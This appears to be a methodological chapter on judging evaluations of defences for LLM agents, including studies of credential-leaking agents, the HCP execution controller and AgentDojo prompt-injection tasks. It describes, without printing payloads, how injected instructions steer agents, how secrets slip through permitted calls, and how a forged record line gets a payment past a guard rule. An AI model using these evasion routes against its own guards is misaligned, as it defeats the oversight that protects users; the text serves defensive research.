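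An agent's behaviour after a refusal can change the result a great deal. *Multi-Aspect Runtime Verification for Simulation-Based V&V of LLM-Enabled Autonomous Agents* (2026) reports 308 simulated delivery runs that included at least one refusal. In 80.5% of them, the planner then made a delivery that followed the rules, and it abandoned the other 60. A replay would have shown the refusals but none of the recoveries, making the gate look much more disruptive than it was. For an agent that looks for a way around the gate, a replay would err in the opposite direction. Tests of self-driving cars face the same problem. *Planning-Oriented End-to-End Autonomous Driving* (2026) distinguishes open-loop tests, which use recorded situations, from closed-loop tests, in which the system's own choices produce the situations it faces next.

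### MCPHunt's correction

Mistaking one kind of test for another can invalidate a published claim. In *MCPHunt*, Li, Sun and colleagues (2026) measured how often agents doing ordinary work, with no attacker, copy passwords and other credentials to places where they do not belong. Their main benchmark has 3,615 recorded runs from five models. They also tested a guard that tracks credentials and blocks attempts to write them elsewhere.

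The submitted version of the paper described the guard's results as a replay over all 3,615 runs. It reported that unsafe writes fell to zero for four of the five models, that blocking rates were consistent across models, and that the guard fully preserved usefulness on tasks that did not require copying a credential. Li and colleagues have withdrawn all these claims. They searched their data and code history and found nothing that reproduces the figures.

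The available evidence came from a live run on one model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash. The guard was active, so a blocked write could change what the agent did next. The evaluation compared 387 guarded runs with unguarded runs of the same tasks from the main benchmark. Credentials reached a forbidden place in 40.1% of unguarded runs and 4.7% of guarded ones, a difference of 35.4 percentage points (95% interval 28.2 to 42.6).

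A live run is in one respect better evidence than a replay, but the guard was not the only difference between these two sets of runs. The researchers collected them about three months apart with different versions of their software, and the task text differed in 345 of the 387 pairs. A true replay would have used identical recordings for both, so the word "replay" implied a control that the study lacked. The phrase "five models" also made the study sound broader than it was. Li and colleagues now describe the figure as an observed difference, not as the effect of the guard.

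They give more weight to a smaller test, in which they ran both versions on the same day with identical task texts. It covers 39 pairs of runs, all involving data from a web browser. The rate fell from 79.5% to 51.3%, a difference of 28.2 points (95% interval 10.8 to 48.8). The guard did not noticeably reduce task completion, but the interval for that difference is wide, from a loss of 15 points to a gain of 21. The software versions still differed, and they ran one set after the other.

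In the larger comparison, all 18 remaining leaks involved browser data. In those runs, credentials also entered through a tool for fetching web pages, which the guard did not treat as a source of secrets. The guarded runs had no leaks in the other eight kinds of task, so a team that tested only those would have reported a perfect guard and missed the same kind of gap that made gate A lose in the earlier example.

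### The case for a simulated comparison

Simulated comparisons also count as evidence, and live ones can mislead. Suppose one company uses gate A and has two leaks in a year, while another uses gate B and has six. If the first company faced 100 attacks and the second faced 1,000, gate B had the lower leak rate, 0.6% against 2%. In practice, neither company is likely to know how many attacks it faced, and the two will also differ in their users, permissions and models. A simulation can give both gates the same calls and permissions, so any difference in their decisions must come from the gates.

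Kekatos and colleagues replay the same recorded behaviour against each defence, so random variation in the model cannot affect the comparison. They replaced a rule that flagged every payment with one that flagged only payments to accounts absent from the user's records. On the banking tasks, detection of successful attacks fell from 79.2% to 70.0%, while false alarms on ordinary runs fell from 44.0% to 24.0%. Those false-alarm rates come from only 25 runs, but across all the recorded models the new rule removed 75 false alarms in 700 runs. It could not have added any, because it flags a subset of what the old rule flags. The useful result is the size of the trade-off, which would have been hard to measure as cleanly with two separate deployments.

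Testing two defences on identical inputs can hide differences between them, as the same study shows. Kekatos and colleagues wrote a stricter version of the payment rule, which accepts an account only if it appears in the result of a lookup the agent itself made. On the original recordings, the two versions had the same detection and false-alarm rates. The researchers then added one line to each flagged run that looked like an entry in the user's records and named the attacker's account. With that line added, the first version accepted 94% of the payments it had flagged, and the stricter version accepted none of them.

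Both comparisons used recordings instead of running an agent. The second was more informative because the researchers considered how an attacker would get past the rule. A team with little money for live tests can also write attacks that target each gate's assumptions and run every attack on both gates.

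## Reading and reporting a study that uses several tiers

When one study uses several kinds of test, readers can easily mistake a number from one experiment for evidence about another. Liu's *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* is useful for practice because it includes scripted and live tests, uses both simulated and real tools, and gives enough detail for readers to check each claim.

The study tests the Handle-Capability Protocol (HCP), a program that sits between an agent and its tools. HCP stores permissions, checks each call against them, and can give the agent a *handle*, a reference that stands for some data without revealing it. Liu compares HCP with an access-control gateway that enforces the same eight security rules but shares none of HCP's policy code. One rule is that a tool's description cannot grant permission to use the tool.

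| Experiment | Tools and effects | Source of the calls | Size |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scripted cases | Simulated | Script | 18 attacks and 25 legitimate workflows |
| AgentDojo tasks | Simulated | Two live models | 344 sessions on 24 tasks |
| AgentDojo follow-up | Simulated | Three other live models | 216 attacked combinations of task, model and defence |
| MCP servers | Real servers, files and local network | Script | 132 conditions |
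| Cost | Real server | Script | 1,000 timed workflows per setting, in each of two passes |

No row combines a live model with real tools. The study therefore provides no direct evidence of how well HCP protects a live agent on a real server, which is what most people choosing a defence want to know.

### Eighteen scripted attacks

All 18 scripted attacks succeeded with no execution checks, and 11 succeeded with a set of common connection checks, such as approval prompts and a check on who owns a note. HCP and the gateway each stopped all 18 attacks and completed all 25 legitimate workflows.

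- Supported: "With simulated tools, HCP and the gateway each prevented all 18 scripted attacks and completed all 25 legitimate workflows."
- Not supported: "HCP blocks 100% of attacks on MCP agents."

Liu built the cases around known security properties, so they test whether each program applies its rules correctly. Because the cases are not a random sample of attacks, an upper limit on the attack success rate calculated from 0 successes out of 18 would mean little.

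The tie also gives no reason to prefer HCP. Liu uses it to argue that the protection comes from enforcing the rules, not from putting them in one central program. The result supports this for the 18 attacks. But the same author wrote both programs and the test cases, so a misunderstanding of a rule could affect all three.

A trial in which the attack's setup fails should be marked inconclusive, as Liu did in one baseline. The simulated user refused every approval prompt, and three attacks succeeded while Liu counted 14 as prevented. The remaining attack replays an earlier approved write, but the refusals had blocked that write, so Liu marked the case inconclusive. The same policy completed only 14 of the 25 legitimate workflows.

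### Sixteen removed checks

Liu then made 16 copies of HCP, each with one check removed, and ran all 43 cases on every copy. Separate targeted tests, each designed to depend on one check, covered weaknesses that the main cases might miss. Some of the results were:

| Check removed | Newly successful attacks, of 18 | Targeted tests that changed |
|---|---:|---:|
| Whether the caller has a matching permission | 6 | 10 |
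| Which note a call will actually open | 0 | 1 |
| Whether the user approved the action | 0, with 3 inconclusive | 1 |
| Whether a saved approval request has expired | 0 | 1 |
| Audit log | 0 | 0 |

Seven of the 16 removals left the number of successful attacks unchanged, but for six of those, a targeted test exposed the missing check. The seventh removed the audit log, which only records decisions. For example, HCP normally determines which note a call will open. When Liu made it rely on the caller's description instead, a targeted test read a note without permission.

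- Supported: "For 15 of the 16 checks, removing the check changed the result of at least one attack or targeted test."
- Not supported: "Seven of the 16 checks are unnecessary."

If the score in an ablation stays the same after a check is removed, that may mean only that another check stopped the same attacks. Liu removed checks only from HCP, so the results do not show how the gateway would behave without those checks.

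### A live model that never tried

In the first AgentDojo experiment, gpt-6.1-sol never attempted the attacker's goal, even without a defence. Since it made no attempts that a defence could stop, the interception rate for this model is undefined, and a results table should show a blank cell instead of 0% or 100%.

- Supported: "gpt-6.1-sol did not attempt the attacker's goal in any of 144 attacked sessions."
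- Not supported: "HCP protected gpt-6.1-sol from prompt injection."

The follow-up used three other models and 24 new tasks. If an attack failed, a language model revised the text once and tried again. None of the models attempted the attacker's goal in any of the 209 combinations that finished. Liu gives a nominal 95% upper limit of 1.8% on the success rate, calculated with the Wilson formula described earlier.

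That limit is calculated from pooled runs with HCP, with the gateway and with no defence. The 71 undefended combinations alone give an upper limit of about 5.1%. Even that figure assumes the combinations are independent, but the same tasks recur across models. The follow-up provides some evidence that these models resist this attacker, but it can't show that either defence stops an attempt.

### Ten blocked calls

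The other model in the first AgentDojo experiment, deepseek-v4-pro, achieved the attacker's goal in only four sessions, all undefended. In the defended sessions, the gateway blocked all seven calls the model made towards such goals, and HCP blocked all three.

The seven calls came from four sessions and the three came from one, so HCP's perfect interception rate with live models is based on a single session. Even if its three calls were independent, the result would be compatible with HCP missing up to 56% of such calls.

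Liu also compared attack success on matched tasks. The average share of sessions in which the attack succeeded fell by 4 percentage points with the gateway and 2 with HCP. Neither difference was statistically significant (p = 0.25 and p = 0.50).

The test calculates how often a result this one-sided would occur if each task were equally likely to change in either direction. Only three tasks changed with the gateway, so even if all three improved, the p-value would be 2 × 0.5³ = 0.25. For HCP, two tasks changed, so the minimum was 0.50. At least six tasks would have to change, all in the same direction, to bring the p-value below 0.05.

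- Supported: "HCP blocked all three attacker calls that deepseek-v4-pro made, all in one session."
- Not supported: "HCP significantly reduced the attack success rate."

The blocked calls show that HCP can stop this model's attempts, but the experiment was too small to estimate how much difference that makes across tasks. It would therefore be equally wrong to conclude from the p-values that HCP had no effect.

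### The effect on legitimate work

Both defences also blocked some legitimate work. With no attack present, gpt-6.1-sol completed 19 of 24 tasks without a defence, 16 with the gateway and 17 with HCP. These differences could be due to chance, but a similar pattern appeared in the follow-up, which had a larger sample. Its three models completed 68 of 69 scored sessions without a defence, 60 of 68 with the gateway and 59 of 67 with HCP.

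The permissions were strict because Liu took them from the benchmark's reference solutions. In the first experiment, the defences refused 40 calls unrelated to the attacks. Most differed from the reference in a detail such as a date, a title or a channel name. A real user might have accepted some of those differences.

Liu examined all 241 refused writes from both AgentDojo experiments. In 219, the call differed in substance from every comparable action in the reference solution, and in another 15, the reference solution never used that tool. These two groups make up 97% of the refusals.

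- Supported: "97% of the refused writes differed in substance from the reference solution or used a tool that it did not use."
- Not supported: "97% of the refusals were correct."

A reference solution is one acceptable way to do a task, and Liu notes that it does not describe all the others. Someone would have to judge the refused calls against what the user wanted before calling the refusals correct.

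### Secrets in permitted calls

In the experiment on real MCP servers, HCP and the gateway blocked writes to files the agent had no permission to write to. However, both allowed calls that sent a secret as ordinary text to a permitted destination, because each call was permitted on its own and neither defence tracked where the text had come from.

Liu tried two remedies. A *session budget* restricts where the agent can send anything after it reads a secret. The alternative is to give the agent only a handle, and to check the secret's label when the agent asks to move the data. Counting the workflows in Liu's results gives:

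| Defence | Forbidden workflows that succeeded | Legitimate workflows refused |
|---|---:|---:|
| None | 8 of 8 | 0 of 6 |
| Separate check on each call | 7 of 8 | 0 of 6 |
| Session budget | 2 of 8 | 4 of 6 |
| Handles | 4 of 9 | 0 of 6 |

The handle row has one extra workflow, a write after an administrator revokes the handle. The counts depend on which workflows Liu chose, so they are not attack success rates, but they do show each remedy's drawbacks. The budget also blocks harmless messages sent after a sensitive read, and handles don't help if the agent already knows the secret. Every defence failed when the secret's label was missing or wrong.

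- Supported: "In prescribed calls to real MCP servers, per-call checks stopped writes without permission but let secrets through to permitted destinations."
- Not supported: "HCP prevents data leaks on real MCP servers."

Handles can block legitimate requests, which this table does not show. In a separate scripted test, Liu configured HCP to return only handles for classified notes, and HCP then refused a legitimate request to display a note. The zero in the last column covers only the six workflows in this experiment.

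### Three answers about speed

The study contains several timing measurements, and they give very different impressions of HCP:

| Measurement | HCP | Gateway | HCP divided by gateway |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Write through a handle, in memory (mean) | 0.0896 ms | 0.0022 ms | 41 |
| Approved write over local HTTP (mean) | 3.38 ms | 2.92 ms | 1.16 |
| File copy on the same real server (median, two passes) | 2.54 and 2.59 ms | 2.38 and 2.30 ms | 1.07 and 1.13 |

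The in-memory test makes HCP look 41 times slower because it leaves out almost everything else that takes time in a real call. The two programs also returned different responses and kept different records in that test, so the gap does not isolate the time HCP's checks take.

For the file copy, Liu kept the server, inputs and responses the same. Without a defence, the copy took a median of 2.28 milliseconds. HCP added 0.26 milliseconds in one pass and 0.31 in the other.

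- Supported: "On one shared machine, with one workflow running at a time, HCP added 0.26 and 0.31 milliseconds to the median file copy in two passes."
- Not supported: "HCP is 41 times slower than the gateway", or "HCP adds 0.3 milliseconds to any tool call."

Memory use may matter more than speed in deployment. HCP's memory use grew by 7.7 MB over 1,000 workflows, compared with 0.7 MB for the gateway, because HCP keeps every task and log entry. Liu did not build a way to export or delete these records. At the same rate, a million workflows would use about 7.7 GB.

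### The abstract and the limitations

In the limitations section, Liu explains that the scripted cases do not estimate how common attacks are, how models respond to adaptive attackers, or how secure other deployed servers are. The section also acknowledges that the AgentDojo accounts are simulated, that the permissions are idealised and that the real servers received prescribed calls. These are the right cautions, but someone who reads only the abstract could miss most of them:

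| Wording in the abstract | Detail needed to interpret it |
|---|---|
| "both controllers block 100% of attacker calls" | Ten calls in five sessions, all from one model |
| "relaxing them admits 4 real exploits" | The four came from approving every refused write, in simulated accounts |
| Handles "block 100% of handle leaks" | Secrets that the agent already knew, or that had no correct label, still got out |
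| More than "25× faster than ChainCaps" | The ratio compares added time, not total time |

The second row is easy to misread. Liu tested three milder changes, which ignored formatting differences such as how a date or city is written, and none of them changed any decisions. The abstract therefore gives no evidence that modestly relaxing the permissions would be dangerous.

The last row concerns ChainCaps, another team's defence, which ran its checks inside the server. ChainCaps added about 30 times as much time as HCP in one pass and 23 times as much in the other, so "more than 25" is true of only the first. Its total time was about four times HCP's. Liu warns in the results that the added time reflects ChainCaps's own analysis and is not a comparison of controllers, but the abstract presents it as one.

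A more careful abstract could still be short. For the first row, it might read: "On 24 simulated tasks, one of two live models attempted the attacker's goal. It succeeded in four undefended sessions, and the two defences blocked all ten of its attacker calls across five other sessions."

### Labels that belong on every table

Each table of results should state which parts were real and where the calls came from, because readers often copy a table without the surrounding text. Tier numbers alone aren't enough, because a higher number doesn't necessarily mean that more of the system is real. In *Agentic Behavior Engineering* (2026), which describes a method for testing business agents, Tier 1 checks the code around the model with prepared model replies. Tiers 2 to 4 all use the same replay process, but differ in how many scenarios they cover, what triggers them and how strictly they block a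 release.

*AgentOrch* (Liu, Huang and colleagues, 2026) is a good example of disclosing which parts of a study were simulated. Its benchmark tests workflows across services such as Slack, Jira and Salesforce. The paper states that the researchers used real connections only to collect reference results and ran every workflow from a model on simulated ones. Without that statement, a reader might assume that the models used the real services. Running their workflows on live services would have sent real messages and changed real records.

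*CARE* goes further by listing the conclusion that each of its test levels supports:

| Level | Supported conclusion |
|---|---|
| Fixture smoke, with a substitute agent | The test environment is internally consistent |
| Live smoke, with the real model on a few cases | The parts work together on those cases |
| Live end-to-end, on a fixed set of scenarios | The system is acceptable within the selected scope |

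All three levels are simulated, with a program controlling the orders and refunds, so "live end-to-end" does not mean real customers. The distinction matters in *CARE*'s own results, where the combined score from simulated conversations rose from 93.29 to 94.39 between the first and second versions of its model. Over the same two periods, real users' satisfaction with the model went from 4.6 points below that of the system it was meant to replace to 8.0 points below. Few users left ratings in the early periods, so the wider gap could be chance, but the higher simulation score wasn't enough to predict an improvement with real users.

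### Counts and inconclusive trials

A study should report each experiment's results out of that experiment's own total and say what is being counted. *From Evidence to Effect* (Li, Xu and colleagues, 2026) tests whether agents publish work only while they still have permission. Its inventory lists the unit and number for each kind of evidence, including 960 deterministic cases built from six recorded executions, 24 live executions, and 468 stage results from 117 longer runs on three tasks. It also identifies which experiments made no paid model calls.

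Li and colleagues add 960 deterministic cases to 128 cases with live models, for a total of 1,088, but they explain that such totals are an inventory and not a statistical sample. A confidence interval that treated the 1,088 cases as independent trials would be far too narrow, because most of them reuse the same six executions.

The choice of total can also hide authorised work that the system failed to complete. One experiment tested the gate in 16 situations where publishing was authorised. The gate allowed all 12 valid requests to publish, but in the other four situations the model had not made a valid request. The gate's result is therefore 12 of 12, but the whole system's result is 12 of 16 because it includes the model's four failures.

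Inconclusive trials need their own column because studies treat them differently. AgentOrch keeps runs that it cannot score and gives them zero for accuracy. Zhu and colleagues record unknown results but leave them out when calculating rates. Giving zero is cautious when the score measures success at a task, but in an attack success rate it would make the defence look better with every crashed run.

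The four successful attacks in the deepseek-v4-pro results were in the undefended condition, where only 17 of the 24 planned sessions ran. The attack success rate was 24% of the sessions that ran. Out of all 24 planned sessions, it would be 17% if the seven missing attacks had all failed and 46% if they had all succeeded. A table of the number of sessions planned, run, successful and inconclusive lets readers work out this range.

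### Versions, untested parts and stronger claims

The version list should cover the model, the agent's software, the defence and its permissions, the protocol revision, the servers and the scoring program. In *CARE*, a run stops if any of the fixed versions changes. Liu's test program will not start if someone has altered a frozen file. Liu also notes that the model names in the follow-up are as reported by the service that supplied the models, a useful caution since a service can change the model behind a name.

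A study should also separate what its authors planned from what they ran. The abstract of *PentestChain* (Patel, Almaiah and colleagues, 2026), a paper on automated security testing, specifies a protocol with three standard benchmarks, at least ten trials per configuration and reruns of two rival systems. The results it gives come only from "the legacy targets measured to date", but a hurried reader could easily think they came from the full protocol.

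Wen, Wang and Xu (2026), in *OpenRath*, avoid this problem in a report on software for running agents. They link their claims to specific tests and records, and list what they have left for later, including broad comparisons and the quality of live model services. The claims table in *Metis* has a similar purpose. It is even more helpful to say what test would support the next claim. For HCP, that list might be:

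| Stronger claim | Evidence it would need |
|---|---|
| HCP lowers the attack success rate for live models | Many more tasks on which undefended models attempt the attack |
| HCP protects a live agent on real MCP servers | The same live model on real servers, with and without HCP |
| HCP prevents leaks through permitted calls | Attacks with missing labels, reworded secrets and secrets the agent already knows, all stopped |
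| HCP is practical in long-term use | Long runs under a realistic load, with old records exported or deleted |

The third row would probably require changes to HCP as well as more tests, since Liu has already shown some of those attacks succeeding.

### A reviewer's checklist

1. Does every table state which tools and effects were real, and whether a script or a live model issued the calls?
2. Did the attacks succeed without the defence, on the same cases?
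3. How many attempts reached the defence, and from how many separate sessions and tasks?
4. Does each percentage have its own total, with repeats and pooled conditions identified?
5. Where are the trials that crashed, timed out or never ran, and how much could they change the result?
6. How much legitimate work did the defence block, and who decided which calls were legitimate?
7. Could someone identify the exact versions and permissions tested?
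8. Does the abstract claim anything that only an untested combination, such as a live model on real servers, could show?
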